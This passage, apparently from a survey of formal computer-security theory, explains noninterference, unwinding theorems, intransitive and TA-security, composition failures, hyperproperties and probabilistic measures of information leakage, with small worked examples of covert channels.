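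A quota on the number of blocks is also not enough if the system reports which block each domain has received and hands out blocks in numerical order. Low then gets block 1 if High has made no request and block 2 if High has made one, even though both are within their quotas. Loepere described this channel too, and suggested allocating blocks in random order, which slows the channel. Reserving particular blocks for each domain would remove it.

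### The unwinding conditions

Nobody can check the security equation directly for a real system, because it covers infinitely many sequences of actions. In *Unwinding and Inference Control*, Goguen and Meseguer (1984) therefore proved an "unwinding theorem", which replaces the equation for multilevel security with a simple condition that is both necessary and sufficient. Rushby's version of the theorem applies to any flow policy and uses three conditions, each concerning a single action.

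The verifier first decides, for each domain u, which states look the same to u. The statement that s and t look the same to u can take the form view(u, s) = view(u, t), where view(u, s) is the part of state s that u can see. The conditions must hold for all states s and t, all actions a and all domains u:

1. Output consistency: view(dom(a), s) = view(dom(a), t) ⇒ output(s, a) = output(t, a). If two states look the same to the domain performing an action, the action returns the same result in both.
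2. Step consistency: view(u, s) = view(u, t) ⇒ view(u, step(s, a)) = view(u, step(t, a)). If two states look the same to a domain, they still look the same after the same action.
3. Local respect: if dom(a) ⇝ u does not hold, then view(u, step(s, a)) = view(u, s). An action by a domain that must not influence u leaves u's view unchanged.

They resemble the conditions in Proof of Separability, which also compare a partition's view before and after a single operation.

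The proof that these conditions guarantee security runs the machine twice, once with the full sequence α and once with purge(α, u). It shows by induction on the length of α that if the two runs start in states that look the same to u, they end in states that look the same to u. If α is empty, there is nothing to prove. Otherwise, consider the first action, a:

- If dom(a) ⇝ u, purging keeps a, so both runs perform it. By step consistency, the resulting states still look the same to u.
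- If dom(a) ⇝ u does not hold, purging deletes a, so only the full run performs it. By local respect, this doesn't change u's view, so the two states still look the same to u.

In both cases the remaining sequence is one action shorter, so the induction hypothesis applies to it. Both runs start in s₀, so they end in states that look the same to u. If u then performs an action, output consistency guarantees the same result in both runs, as the security equation requires.

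In the shared-disk example, the natural choice for Low's view is the number of free blocks. Output consistency holds because this number determines whether Low's request succeeds, and step consistency holds because each successful request lowers it by one. But a request by High also lowers it, so the design breaks local respect. If Low's view instead contains only the blocks that Low itself holds, High's requests no longer change it. However, output consistency then fails, because a full disk and an empty one can look the same to Low and still give different replies. No view can satisfy all three conditions, since the theorem would then prove an insecure system secure.

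With quotas, the proof succeeds. Low's view is the number of blocks left in its own quota. That number determines Low's replies, and High's requests never change it. High's view can be the whole state, because the policy allows High to see everything.

Rushby also proved that the method is complete for this definition, meaning that every secure system has views that satisfy the conditions. In his construction, two reachable states look the same to u if no sequence of future actions, followed by an action of u, could produce different results for u. Output consistency and step consistency follow directly. For local respect, suppose the machine reached s by performing a sequence β, and a is an action that must not influence u. If the same actions follow β and β · a, purging for u makes the two sequences identical. In a secure system they must therefore produce the same results for u, so s and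 step(s, a) look the same to u.

Even with completeness, the views are not easy to find, because the constructed view refers to every possible future of the machine, which the verifier wanted to avoid examining. Millen saw the choice of view as the practical weakness of unwinding, since a poor choice brings back the false alarms of information flow analysis. In the disk with quotas, for example, High's requests break local respect if the verifier includes the total number of free blocks in Low's view, even though Low cannot learn that number. A failed proof can therefore mean either that the system leaks or that the verifier chose the wrong view.

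Gligor suggested labelling each variable with a security level and letting a process's view consist of all variables at or below its own level. Rushby gave some support for such nested views. He showed that for any transitive policy (one in which u ⇝ v and v ⇝ w imply u ⇝ w), suitable views exist in which each domain sees everything that the domains allowed to influence it can see.

Even so, Gligor was cautious about using the method on real kernels. It needs a formal specification or source code. Applying it by hand to a system of significant size was impractical, and in 1993 no automated tools could handle a system that large. He thought it best suited to showing that trusted processes are isolated, and less suited to a kernel with many shared variables. Analysts had nevertheless used it to find covert channels in LOCK, a high-assurance system built around the Logical Co-processing Kernel.

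### Reference monitors and multilevel policies

The definition of noninterference mentions no mechanism, but Rushby used the unwinding theorem to show when a reference monitor enforces it. He divided the machine's state into named storage locations. For each domain u, observe(u) is the set of locations whose values u may observe, and alter(u) is the set of locations whose values u may change. These two sets correspond to the monitor's access table. For the table to mean anything, the machine has to satisfy what Rushby called the reference monitor assumptions:

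- The result of an action depends only on locations that the domain performing it may observe.
- When an action changes a location, the new value depends only on locations that the domain may observe.
- An action changes only locations that the domain may alter.

Rushby's assumption about new values applies only to locations that an action changes in at least one of two states. If the two states look the same to the domain performing the action, each such location must have the same value in both states afterwards. Requiring this of every location would be too strong, because the states may already differ in a location that the domain cannot observe. If the action leaves that location alone, the difference remains, but no information has moved.

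The assumptions are stricter than security requires. For example, a low-level user who can add a line to the end of a secret log but can't read the log learns nothing by adding one. The action still violates the assumption about new values, because the log's new contents depend on its old contents, which the user is not allowed to observe.

Rushby proved that a machine satisfying the assumptions is secure if its access table meets two further requirements. The first is that if u ⇝ v, then v may observe everything u may observe. The second is that if u may alter a location that v may observe, then u ⇝ v. To prove this, Rushby defined each domain's view as the contents of the locations it may observe, then checked the three unwinding conditions.

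This shows where a conventional monitor goes wrong on the shared disk. An access table for files would probably have no entry for the count of free blocks. But High's requests change the count and Low's replies depend on it, so the assumptions require the table to record that High may alter it and Low may observe it. The policy would then have to allow High ⇝ Low, which it forbids.

The requirement about observation is easy to meet for military classifications, where people at higher levels may read whatever people at lower levels may read. In a multilevel policy, each domain has a clearance, and u ⇝ v holds exactly when v's clearance dominates u's. Dominance is transitive, so all multilevel policies are transitive. Rushby proved the converse, that all transitive policies are multilevel, and credited Dorothy Denning with an essentially similar result from 1976.

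A transitive policy can be expressed as a multilevel one by assigning labels to its domains. Two domains share a label only if each may influence the other, and one label dominates another if domains with the second label may influence domains with the first. For example, an editor and a spelling checker may influence each other, and both may influence an archive, which may not influence either. The editor and the checker share a label, and the archive's label dominates it. The policy then has the form of a two-level military classification, even though it was not designed for secrecy. The policy of Rushby's encryption device is not transitive, so it cannot be expressed this way, and the 1982 definition fails on such intransitive policies.

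Rushby also derived the Bell-LaPadula rules for multilevel policies from his theorem. If a machine satisfies the reference monitor assumptions and has a fixed table that prevents reading up and writing down, it satisfies noninterference. Real systems could still leak information while obeying the rules, and Rushby attributed these leaks to two gaps in the original model.

One gap is that Bell and LaPadula never defined what it means to observe or alter an object. A designer could deliberately swap the two meanings, so that the rule against reading up would let subjects alter only objects below their own level. A designer can also accidentally overlook an indirect way of observing something. Gligor's example is the UNIX command for removing a directory, which fails if the directory still contains files. Suppose that a low-level user has created a directory for high-level files inside a low-level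 one. A high-level process can add or remove files there, and the low-level user can find out whether the directory is empty by trying to remove it. The result depends on something that the user is not allowed to observe, which violates the assumption about results. Multics did not have this channel because it allowed users to remove directories that still contained files.

The other gap is that Bell and LaPadula's model did not treat the access table and the monitor's other internal data as objects, so the ban on writing down did not apply to them. This is how the MITRE kernel could satisfy the model and still leak through its disk quota. Users change the access table when they create files and grant each other access, and Bell and LaPadula wrote a set of rules for these operations on Multics. Landwehr wrote in 1981 that the final Bell-LaPadula rules contained no storage channels, but Rushby,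 citing work from 1983 and 1984, reported that two of the rules for Multics were known to permit insecure flows.

Rushby's result avoids the problem only because the access table in his model cannot change. For systems where the table can change, he recommended checking the unwinding conditions directly for each operation that modifies the table or other internal data.

Noninterference is less strict than the Bell-LaPadula rules in at least one respect. According to Purdue University's notes, it allows a low-level user to copy one high-level file into another, as long as the user learns nothing about the contents. The Bell-LaPadula rules forbid this as reading up.

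## Flow allowed only through an intermediary, 1986 to 2016

In Rushby's encryption device, data from the red component may reach the black component only through the crypto or the censor. The 1982 notation seems to express this easily, with a policy that allows red ⇝ crypto, red ⇝ censor, crypto ⇝ black and censor ⇝ black, and forbids every other influence between different components. This policy is intransitive because it allows red ⇝ crypto and crypto ⇝ black but forbids red ⇝ black.

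Under the 1982 definition, however, no useful device can satisfy this policy, because what black sends to the network has to depend on what red received from the host. Suppose red passes a message to the crypto, the crypto encrypts it and black fetches the result. Purging for black deletes red's action but keeps the crypto's. The crypto then has no message to encrypt, so black fetches something else and the security equation fails. Adding red ⇝ black to the policy would remove the conflict, but red could then send cleartext straight to black. Rushby concluded in his 1992 report that forbidding red to influence black is too strong a requirement and allowing it is too weak.

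He found only one plausible way for a system to satisfy such a policy under the old definition. The intermediary would have to consist of two isolated halves, one that receives from red and one that sends to black, so that nothing passes from red to black. It would then be more natural to list the halves as separate domains, which makes the policy transitive again.

Multilevel systems have the same problem whenever information needs to move from a higher level to a lower one. Eggert, Schnoor and colleagues (2013), in *Complexity and Unwinding for Intransitive Noninterference*, give the examples of distributing battle plans and replying to freedom-of-information requests. Designers give this task to a downgrader, a trusted component that decides what to release, as the security officer did in the ACCAT Guard. High may influence the downgrader and the downgrader may influence Low, but High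 must not influence Low directly.

### The intransitive purge

Goguen and Meseguer's 1982 paper included a way to describe intermediaries, but it was incorrect. They recognised this and proposed several extensions in 1984. Rushby credited the first satisfactory treatment to Haigh and Young (1986), in *Extending The Non-Interference Version Of MLS For Sat*. Haigh and Young worked at Honeywell on the Secure Ada Target, a high-assurance computer that had to enforce both multilevel security and a policy of fixed routes between programs. They published a more polished version in 1987 under nearly the same title.

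They proposed purging fewer actions. If u may reach v only through w, purging for v should delete an action of u only if no action of w follows it. If one does follow, u's action stays, because w could legitimately have passed its effects on to v.

Haigh and Young described this rule informally, and Rushby turned it into two functions. The set sources(α, u) contains u and every domain from which information could reach u during the sequence α, using only permitted influences and in the order in which the actions occur:

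- sources(Λ, u) = {u}.
- sources(a · α, u) = sources(α, u) ∪ {dom(a)} if dom(a) ⇝ v for some v in sources(α, u).
- sources(a · α, u) = sources(α, u) otherwise.

The intransitive purge, ipurge, keeps an action only if its domain is in this set:

- ipurge(Λ, u) = Λ.
- ipurge(a · α, u) = a · ipurge(α, u) if dom(a) is in sources(a · α, u).
- ipurge(a · α, u) = ipurge(α, u) otherwise.

The security equation has the same form as before, with ipurge in place of purge:

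test(α, a) = test(ipurge(α, dom(a)), a)

For a transitive policy, the two purges give the same result. If such a policy lets information reach u through a chain of domains, it also lets the first domain in the chain influence u directly, so the ordinary purge already keeps that domain's actions. Rushby therefore suggested treating the intransitive definition as basic and the 1982 definition as a special case.

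He illustrated the new definition with a machine that has three registers, u, v and x, all initially zero. Each of its four domains has one action:

- U sets u to 1.
- V sets v to 2.
- W sets x to the sum of u and v.
- X outputs the value of x.

U and V may influence W, and W may influence X, but U and V must not influence X directly. The machine satisfies this policy because information about u and v reaches X only when W copies their sum. In an insecure variant, X outputs u + v directly. The table gives X's output in both machines after three sequences of actions, with each action written as the name of its domain.

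| Actions so far | After intransitive purge for X | Original, actual output | Original, output after purge | Variant, actual output | Variant, output after purge |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| UV | Λ | 0 | 0 | 3 | 0 |
| UWV | UW | 1 | 1 | 3 | 1 |
| UVW | UVW | 3 | 3 | 3 | 3 |

After U and V act, X reads 0 in the original machine, and deleting both actions makes no difference. In the variant, X reads 3 without the purge and 0 with it, so the equation fails, which reveals the leak. If W acts last, the purge deletes nothing and the two machines give the same results. If W acts between U and V, it can pass on U's action but not V's, so the purge deletes only V's.

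The original machine also fails the 1982 definition. The ordinary purge keeps only W's action from the sequence UVW, so W adds two zeros and X reads 0 instead of 3.

### Weak step consistency

To prove that a system satisfies the new definition, a verifier again needs conditions on single actions. Rushby kept output consistency and local respect from the ordinary unwinding theorem and replaced step consistency with a weaker condition. Weak step consistency requires, for all states s and t, actions a and domains u:

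view(u, s) = view(u, t) and view(dom(a), s) = view(dom(a), t) ⇒ view(u, step(s, a)) = view(u, step(t, a))

Weak step consistency allows the change in what a domain sees to depend on what the acting domain sees, as well as on what the first domain already sees. In the register machine, U sees register u, V sees v, X sees x, and W sees both u and v. Ordinary step consistency fails because two states can have the same x but different sums for W to copy into x. Weak step consistency holds because the new x depends only on the registers that W sees. Local respect also holds because U and V change nothing that X sees.

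In the variant, no choice of views satisfies both output consistency and local respect. X outputs u + v, so output consistency requires X's view to determine that sum. An action by U can change the sum and therefore X's view, which violates local respect.

The proof again compares a full run with a purged one. In the ordinary theorem, it was enough for the two runs to keep looking the same to u. Here they have to look the same to every domain in sources(α, u), where α is the part of the sequence still to come. Let a be the next action:

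- If the purge keeps a, consider any domain v in sources(α, u). If dom(a) ⇝ v, then dom(a) was itself in the set before the step, so the two states look the same to dom(a) as well as to v. By weak step consistency, they still look the same to v after a. If dom(a) must not influence v, local respect leaves v's view unchanged in both runs.
- If the purge deletes a, then dom(a) must not influence any domain in sources(α, u). By local respect, performing a in only one of the runs changes none of their views.

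At the end of the sequence only u remains in the set, so the final states look the same to u, and output consistency completes the proof. Rushby checked the argument with the EHDM theorem prover because earlier attempts at this theory had failed.

The theorem also removes one of Rushby's two requirements for access tables, that if u ⇝ v, then v may observe everything u may observe. In the encryption device, this requirement would let the crypto observe everything red observes and black observe everything the crypto observes, so red could keep nothing from black. The remaining requirement lets red write to a buffer that the crypto reads, and the crypto write to a buffer that black reads, as long as red cannot write to anything black reads.

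Haigh and Young also had an unwinding theorem, but Rushby thought it was probably wrong or of very little use. They kept ordinary step consistency but changed local respect, requiring that any action "purgeable" with respect to u leave u's view unchanged. Whether an action is purgeable depends on the actions that follow it, but their condition did not include a sequence of actions. The published proof was only a sketch and did not make clear what they meant.

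Rushby reasoned that if their condition was stricter than local respect, the theorem would cover fewer systems than the ordinary one, although it was meant to cover more. If the condition was less strict, some actions could change the views of domains they must not influence, and he could not see how the two remaining conditions would keep such changes within safe limits. In the register machine, for example, ordinary step consistency seems to force u and v into X's view, because W's action makes x depend on them. It is then hard to see how the theorem could distinguish the secure machine from the variant. Without an exact definition of the condition, Rushby could not prove the theorem false.

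### What the intermediary releases

Once an intermediary has acted, the intransitive purge keeps all earlier actions of the domains that may influence the intermediary, whatever that action was. Suppose High writes two files and the downgrader orders the release of one, but a fault in the machine gives both to Low. Purging for Low deletes nothing, so both sides of the security equation describe the same run, and the equation holds despite the leak.

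Roscoe and Goldsmith (1999), in *What is intransitive noninterference?*, objected that the definition was too weak. According to van der Meyden (2007), in *A comparison of semantic models for intransitive noninterference*, they had tried and failed to use it to reason about a downgrader. They proposed an alternative based on determinism, in which High's behaviour must not introduce any uncertainty into what Low sees.

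Van der Meyden translated Rushby's machines into Roscoe and Goldsmith's notation and found that, under one translation, one of their two alternative definitions amounts to the 1982 definition applied to an intransitive policy. This definition detects the release of the wrong file, but it also rejects a machine that correctly copies the right file on the downgrader's command, because purging High's actions empties the file. It would accept an officer who reads High's message on one screen and retypes it for Low, because the purge keeps the officer's typing. The definition might therefore suit a human reviewer, but it does not suit the crypto, which has to process red's data inside the machine.

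Von Oheimb (2004) defended intransitive noninterference as valid and useful in practice. He attributed at least part of Roscoe and Goldsmith's difficulty to implementation errors they had assumed, not to intransitivity. Releasing a file that nobody requested does seem to be an implementation error, but verification is supposed to find such errors, and proving intransitive noninterference would not reveal this one.

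The policy describes only the routes information may take. It ensures that information passes through the intermediary, but not that the intermediary releases the right things. An encryption component that forwarded every message in cleartext would satisfy the policy, as would a censor that let everything through. Rushby noted in 1992 that specifying what these components must do is a separate problem.

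The case for the encryption device therefore needs three proofs: that red can reach black only through the crypto and the censor, that the crypto encrypts everything it sends, and that the censor enforces its rules on headers. Red and black need no verification, as in Rushby's original argument for the design.

### The order of two secret events

Van der Meyden's own objection to the intransitive purge concerns information that no intermediary had. In his example, two secret domains, H1 and H2, each have their own downgrader, D1 and D2. The policy allows H1 ⇝ D1 ⇝ L and H2 ⇝ D2 ⇝ L, but no flow between the two sides. Suppose H1 and H2 each write a document, D1 and D2 release them, and L's inbox lists the released documents in the order in which H1 and H2 wrote them.

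Let h1 and h2 stand for writing the documents, and d1 and d2 for releasing them. The inbox lists H1's document first after h1 h2 d1 d2, and H2's first after h2 h1 d1 d2. D1 and D2 may each know only what happens on their own side, so neither can tell which document came first. They could not work it out even by combining their knowledge, because the system has no shared clock. But L can read the order from the inbox.

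The intransitive purge does not detect this. A release follows each document, so purging for L leaves both sequences unchanged, including the order of the documents. The definition therefore allows L to see different results for the two sequences. It protects a document that nobody has released, but once both documents are released, it treats their original order as released too.

Van der Meyden (2008), in *On Notions of Causality and Distributed Knowledge*, stated the principle behind the objection. Whatever a domain knows about others should follow from the combined knowledge of the domains that may influence it. To capture this, he had already defined a function, ta, that records the most a domain may know about a sequence of actions. The name refers to the transmission of information about actions:

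- ta(Λ, u) = Λ.
- ta(α · a, u) = ta(α, u) if dom(a) ⇝ u does not hold. The new action adds nothing to u's record.
- ta(α · a, u) = (ta(α, u), ta(α, dom(a)), a) otherwise. The new record contains u's old record, the record of the domain that acted, and the action itself.

A system is TA-secure if each domain gets the same results after any two action sequences that leave it with the same record. In symbols, if ta(α, u) = ta(β, u), then test(α, a) = test(β, a) for every action a of u.

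In the example, D1's record after both documents exist is (Λ, Λ, h1), whichever was created first, because H2's action adds nothing to it. Similarly, D2's record is (Λ, Λ, h2), and L's is still Λ. After d1, L's record becomes (Λ, (Λ, Λ, h1), d1). After d2, it becomes ((Λ, (Λ, Λ, h1), d1), (Λ, Λ, h2), d2). L's final record is the same whichever document was created first, so TA-security requires L to see the same inbox in both cases. The system violates this requirement. Sorting the inbox by release date would fix the system, because L is allowed to learn the order of d1 and d2.

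TA-security is stricter than the definition based on the intransitive purge, but the two are equivalent for transitive policies. Van der Meyden also defined an even stricter version, TO-security, in which an intermediary can pass on only what it has observed. If a downgrader's command reveals to Low whether High has acted, but the downgrader itself never finds out, the system violates TO-security. It can still satisfy TA-security, because the policy allowed the downgrader to know.

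Eggert and colleagues proved that no algorithm can decide for every finite-state system whether it meets the stricter definition, TO-security. They gave algorithms for checking the 1982 definition, the intransitive purge and TA-security, with running times that grow only polynomially with the size of the system. These algorithms also produce a counterexample when a system is insecure, and the verifier does not have to find suitable views.

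### Why Rushby's conditions prove TA-security

In 1992 Rushby proved that his three conditions guarantee security in the sense of the intransitive purge. The converse, that every secure system has views satisfying them, is false, as the inbox example shows. When D2 releases its document, L's inbox changes in a way that depends on which document H1 or H2 wrote first. Neither L's view nor D2's can contain that information without breaking local respect or weak step consistency earlier in the run, so no choice of views satisfies all three conditions.

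Van der Meyden (2015) showed that the same conditions are both sound and complete for TA-security. Soundness means that any system satisfying them is TA-secure. Under weak step consistency, what u sees after an action depends on what u saw before, what the acting domain saw, and which action it performed. The function ta combines exactly these three things in u's record. Local respect corresponds to the rule that a forbidden action adds nothing to the record. By induction on the length of the sequences, two runs that give u the same record therefore lead to states that look the same to u, so the system is TA-secure.

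The converse, completeness, needs a small change to the machine. Two different sequences can lead to the same state while giving u different records, so the verifier first makes the machine store its whole history in its state, which does not affect any output. Each state is then reached by only one sequence α, and u's view of that state can be defined as the record ta(α, u). Local respect and weak step consistency follow from the definition of ta, and output consistency is the definition of TA-security.

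A system whose access table fits the policy is TA-secure. Conversely, van der Meyden proved that any TA-secure system can be interpreted as enforcing such a table.

### Policies that change during operation

All these definitions assume a fixed policy, but permissions change when people move to new jobs, administrators revoke privileges, or operators respond to an attack. In *Dynamic Intransitive Noninterference*, Leslie extended Rushby's framework to systems whose users can set up domains while the system is running. She kept his unwinding theorem and added a condition, called policy respect, to cover the changing policy. Eggert and several colleagues later developed another version with a complete proof method. In *Dynamic Intransitive Noninterference Revisited*, Eggert and van der Meyden (2016) pointed out that both versions miss the leak of the order of events because they use forms of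 the intransitive purge.

Eggert and van der Meyden extended TA-security instead and found two reasonable ways to do it, one giving priority to the influences the current policy permits and the other to those it forbids. The choice makes no difference under a fixed policy, which forbids whatever it does not permit, but permissions and prohibitions can conflict when the policy changes.

For example, suppose an administrator can open and close a connection from B to C. The policy permits B to send to C while the connection is open, but forbids C from learning anything about the administrator's actions. When a message from B arrives, C learns that the administrator has opened the connection. The system can therefore enforce the prohibition only by blocking messages that the policy permits.

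Eggert and van der Meyden showed that the two readings agree exactly when the policy meets a condition they call locality. Roughly, the sender and the receiver must always be able to tell, by combining what each is permitted to know, whether the policy currently permits flow from the sender to the receiver. In the example, letting B and C know whether their connection is open would remove the conflict, but it would also tell them something about the administrator's actions.

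Eggert and van der Meyden gave sound and complete unwinding conditions for local policies. They also extended Rushby's result on access tables from fixed tables to tables that change along with the policy. They then applied the theory to a simple system, modelled on the Flume operating system, in which programs hold and pass on capabilities (tokens that give their holder a right). They proved that this system enforces the changing flow policy that its capabilities define.

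## Nondeterminism, probability and partial leaks, 1987 to 2010

The definitions so far assume that a machine always gives the same result after the same actions. Many systems are nondeterministic, meaning the same inputs can lead to different outputs. A scheduler may run two programs in either order, a component may use random numbers, or a specification may leave a choice to the programmer. The full run and the purged run could then each end in several ways, so there is no single pair of results to compare in the security equation.

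### Definitions based on possibility

The first generalisations, called possibilistic, compared what Low could possibly see and ignored how likely it was. McCullough (1987) formulated the best-known one, generalized noninterference, in *Specifications for Multi-Level Security and a Hook-Up Property*. In the version in McLean (1994), *A General Theory of Composition for Trace Sets Closed Under Selective Interleaving*, a system is secure if, for every two runs t₁ and t₂, it also has a run t₃ with the High inputs of t₁ and the Low inputs and outputs of t₂. Whatever Low sees is then compatible with anything High might have entered.

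A definition of noninterference for nondeterministic systems has to compare everything Low has seen, whereas checking only the latest observation is enough in deterministic systems. Engelhardt, van der Meyden and Zhang (2012), in *Intransitive Noninterference in Nondeterministic Systems*, describe a machine from which Low reads two digits, each of them 1 or 2. The digits differ if High has done nothing and match if High has acted, so Low can compare them to learn whether High has acted. Because each digit on its own can be 1 or 2 in both cases, the machine still satisfies a definition that checks only the latest observation.

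Compatibility can also be too weak when High sees something before acting. Suppose a machine picks a random bit, shows it to High, and then takes a bit from High. It sends Low a 0 if the two bits are equal and a 1 if they differ. Low could receive either value whatever High enters, so the machine satisfies compatibility. But because High has seen the random bit, it can always choose an input that sends Low the value it wants. Wittbold and Johnson identified this problem and instead required Low's possible views to be the same whatever strategy High follows. Van der Meyden and Zhang (2008), in *A Comparison of Semantic Models for Noninterference*, proved that their change makes no difference in asynchronous systems, where High's actions can always come later, but does matter when both sides act in step.

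### Two secure systems that leak when connected

McCullough found that two systems can both satisfy generalized noninterference and still leak when connected to each other. His counterexample, as McLean retells it, uses two components, A and B, which answer each message from High with an output. Low can send A a cancel command, which A passes to B. Each component may then report "nothing to cancel" to Low only if it has answered all its High messages, and even then it does not have to.

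Each component is secure on its own. A report reveals nothing about High's inputs, because the component could have received any number of messages and answered them all in time.

When A's answers become B's High inputs and B's answers go back to A, a single message from High circulates forever. If messages and commands pass between the components instantly, one component is always holding the message when the cancel command reaches it. Low can therefore receive both reports only if High has sent nothing.

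McLean added probabilities to the example. The table assumes that a component with nothing to cancel reports this half the time and that a circulating message is equally likely to be in A or B.

| Reports Low receives | High has sent nothing | A High message is circulating |
|---|---|---|
| Neither | 25% | 50% |
| Only A's | 25% | 25% |
| Only B's | 25% | 25% |
| Both | 25% | 0% |

A Trojan horse can signal by sending a message or holding it back. McLean put the capacity of this channel, the highest rate at which it can carry information reliably, at about 0.17 bits per symbol, though the percentages in the table give 0.16. Each component leaks nothing on its own if it answers messages faster than the Trojan horse can send them, because it then reports half the time whatever High does.

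McLean traced the failure to feedback. Generalized noninterference requires that for every two runs a third exists, but connecting two components in a loop eliminates some runs, because each component's output has to match the other's input. The property still holds if A sends output to B and receives none back. Zakinthinos and Lee (1995) proved McCullough's conjecture that noninterference composes without feedback, and gave a method for composing components with feedback that preserves it.

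The alternative is to require a stronger property. McCullough (1990), in *A hookup theorem for multilevel security*, recommended restrictiveness, which a system has if all its parts have it. McLean proposed separability, which requires every High history, including outputs, to be compatible with every Low history. Separability is simpler than restrictiveness and also still holds when components are connected with feedback. McLean compared it to Rushby's separation kernel. However, it rules out systems in which Low affects High, such as one that records Low's activity in an audit file and sends the file out on a High channel.

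Rafnsson and Sabelfeld showed in *Compositional Information-flow Security for Interactive Systems* that parallel composition also fails to preserve the condition enforced by practical tools such as Jif and SPARK Examiner. Partitions that exchange requests and replies form a loop, so possibilistic proofs about each partition do not by themselves show that the combination is secure.

### The refinement problem

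Developers often start with a specification that leaves choices open, then settle them one by one. Each step is a refinement, meaning that every run of the new system was already a possible run of the old one. Refinement therefore preserves any requirement on individual runs.

However, refining a specification by removing some of the runs it allows can destroy security. Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, give the example of a specification that lets a system output 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit h. It passes a possibilistic test because a low-security observer could see 0 or 1 whatever h is. A program that always outputs h correctly implements this specification but leaks the whole secret. The specification was secure only because it allowed runs whose output differs from h, and the programmer was free to remove them.

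Clarkson and Schneider showed that refinement preserves exactly those properties that are closed under subsets, meaning that if a set of runs has the property, so does every subset of it. Generalized noninterference is not closed under subsets, because a subset may contain t₁ and t₂ but not t₃.

Observational determinism requires that whenever two runs start in states that look the same to Low, everything Low sees afterwards is also the same. It is closed under subsets, because removing runs cannot create a pair that violates this requirement. Refinement that only removes runs therefore preserves it. The proof of the seL4 kernel later used a property that refinement also preserves, so that security proved for the specification would carry over to the implementation.

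Observational determinism would have rejected the three-way specification at the outset, because Low can see different outputs from the same starting state. It would also reject a program that shows Low the result of a harmless coin toss, or a scheduler whose choices are visible to Low but do not depend on secrets. Clarkson and Schneider considered some visible nondeterminism useful, so they saw this strictness as a drawback.

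### Probabilistic noninterference

Possibilistic definitions can also miss probabilistic leaks, even if nobody refines the system. Suppose a secret bit is equally likely to be 0 or 1, and a system sends Low the correct bit 99% of the time and the flipped bit otherwise. Both outputs are possible for both secrets, so the system passes, even though Low can guess the secret correctly 99% of the time.

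Shannon's information theory measures how much Low learns. It defines the uncertainty of a random quantity as the sum of p × log₂(1/p) over its possible values, where p is the probability of each value. A fair bit has an uncertainty of 1 bit. After Low sees the output, one value of the secret has probability 0.99 and the other 0.01, so the remaining uncertainty is:

0.99 × log₂(1/0.99) + 0.01 × log₂(1/0.01) ≈ 0.0144 + 0.0664 = 0.0808 bits

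The system has therefore revealed 1 − 0.0808 ≈ 0.92 bits of a one-bit secret.

McLean's *Security Models and Information Flow* gave a more realistic example. A command prints on Low's terminal either something High typed earlier or a random string. Any printout could be random, so the system satisfies generalized noninterference, but Low is unlikely to mistake a readable sentence for a random string.

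McLean proposed a probabilistic condition, which he called the Flow Model. Let Lₜ be the values of all Low objects at time t. For every t, the model requires:

P(Lₜ | Low's past and High's past) = P(Lₜ | Low's past)

Knowing what High did earlier must not help anyone who already knows Low's history predict what Low sees now. The condition still allows information to flow from Low to High.

McLean warned that a statistical connection is not always a leak. For example, a system might write each value to a High audit file before writing it to a Low file, so that a user cannot crash the machine before the audit record exists. The audit file then predicts the Low file without influencing it. The Flow Model arguably handles this case, because Low's earlier actions already predict the value, but McLean left open whether it handles more elaborate ones.

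James Gray, who also worked at the Naval Research Laboratory, developed probabilistic noninterference. Gray (1992) provided a general model of probabilistic systems and gave two definitions of information flow security for it. Clarkson and Schneider formulate Gray's condition as follows. For any two initial states s₁ and s₂ that look the same to Low, and every finite sequence ℓ of Low's inputs and outputs:

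P(ℓ | the system starts in s₁) = P(ℓ | the system starts in s₂)

If the initial state contains the secret bit, the 99% system fails the condition because Low receives a 1 with probability 0.99 if the secret is 1, but only 0.01 if it is 0. The three-way specification also fails if the system picks each option a third of the time, because Low then receives a 1 with probability 2/3 or 1/3, depending on h. A system that encrypts the secret bit with a random one-bit key, flipping it exactly half the time without revealing when, satisfies the condition. McLean noted that a probabilistic definition can accept encryption, which the 1982 definition rejects, by treating it as random noise.

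The main disadvantage of probabilistic models is that the verifier has to know the probabilities. Designers may not know how often a scheduler will choose each program, and Clarkson and Schneider give this as one reason for using possibilistic models. Probabilistic proofs also take more work, as Hoang, McIver and colleagues discuss in *Abstractions of non-interference security*. In *A Logical Approach to Multilevel Security of Probabilistic Systems*, Gray and Syverson devised a logic to support such reasoning, which can express time, probability and knowledge.

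### Properties of sets of runs

On the shared disk, a run in which Low receives the reply "full" reveals a leak only when compared with a run in which High made no requests. Clarkson and Schneider built a general theory around this observation.

Clarkson and Schneider call a set of permitted runs a trace property. A system whose set of runs is T satisfies a trace property P if every run in T is also in P, or T ⊆ P. Access control is a trace property, because an inspector can check each run separately for forbidden operations. A hyperproperty is a set of permitted systems, each represented by its full set of runs, and a system satisfies the hyperproperty **H** if T ∈ **H**. Noninterference has to be stated as a hyperproperty, because whether a system may have one run depends on which other runs it has. All the information-flow policies that Clarkson and Schneider examined were hyperproperties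 and not trace properties.

Testing runs one at a time therefore cannot establish noninterference, even if every run looks acceptable. Comparing runs helps more with some definitions than with others:

- For observational determinism, two runs can prove a violation. If they start the same for Low and then differ, no further run can repair this. Finding no such pair proves nothing about the runs that nobody tested.
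- For generalized noninterference, a finite number of tests cannot even prove a violation. The missing t₃ might appear in the next test.
- For probabilistic noninterference, a tester sees how often each output occurs but not its exact probability. A small difference in frequency could be a leak or chance.

A proof has to relate several runs to one another. The unwinding conditions do this by comparing pairs of states. Self-composition instead runs a program P and then a copy P′ with every variable renamed. The verifier proves that if the Low variables of P and P′ start with equal values, they also end with equal values, whatever the High variables contain. This turns a statement about two runs of P into one about a single run of the combined program, which ordinary verification methods can handle.

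Clarkson and Schneider extended the method to any requirement whose violations can each be demonstrated with at most k runs, using k copies of the system. For example, a system that splits a secret into k shares must never output all of them, even across separate runs. They had no complete method for requirements without such a limit, or for conditions like generalized noninterference that require certain runs to exist.

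### Measuring partial leaks

Some systems cannot avoid revealing part of a secret. When a login program rejects a wrong password, the user learns that the correct password is something else. McLean pointed out that designers also tolerate messages about available storage or the status of devices, because removing every such leak can slow the system too much. Designers who accept some leaks need to know how much information the system reveals.

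Shannon information, as used for the 99% system, is one measure of a partial leak. Gray applied it to covert channels by treating the leak from High to Low as a communication channel and calculating its capacity. In *A probabilistic approach to information hiding*, McIver and Morgan connected Shannon's theory to programs that make random choices and derived conditions for hiding data.

Shannon information is an average, however, so it can hide a serious risk. Suppose one system prints a random 64-bit key one time in eight and otherwise prints "no key", while another always prints the key's first 8 bits. Both leak 8 bits by Shannon's measure, but an attacker has a one-in-eight chance of obtaining the entire key from the first system and almost no chance of guessing it from the second.

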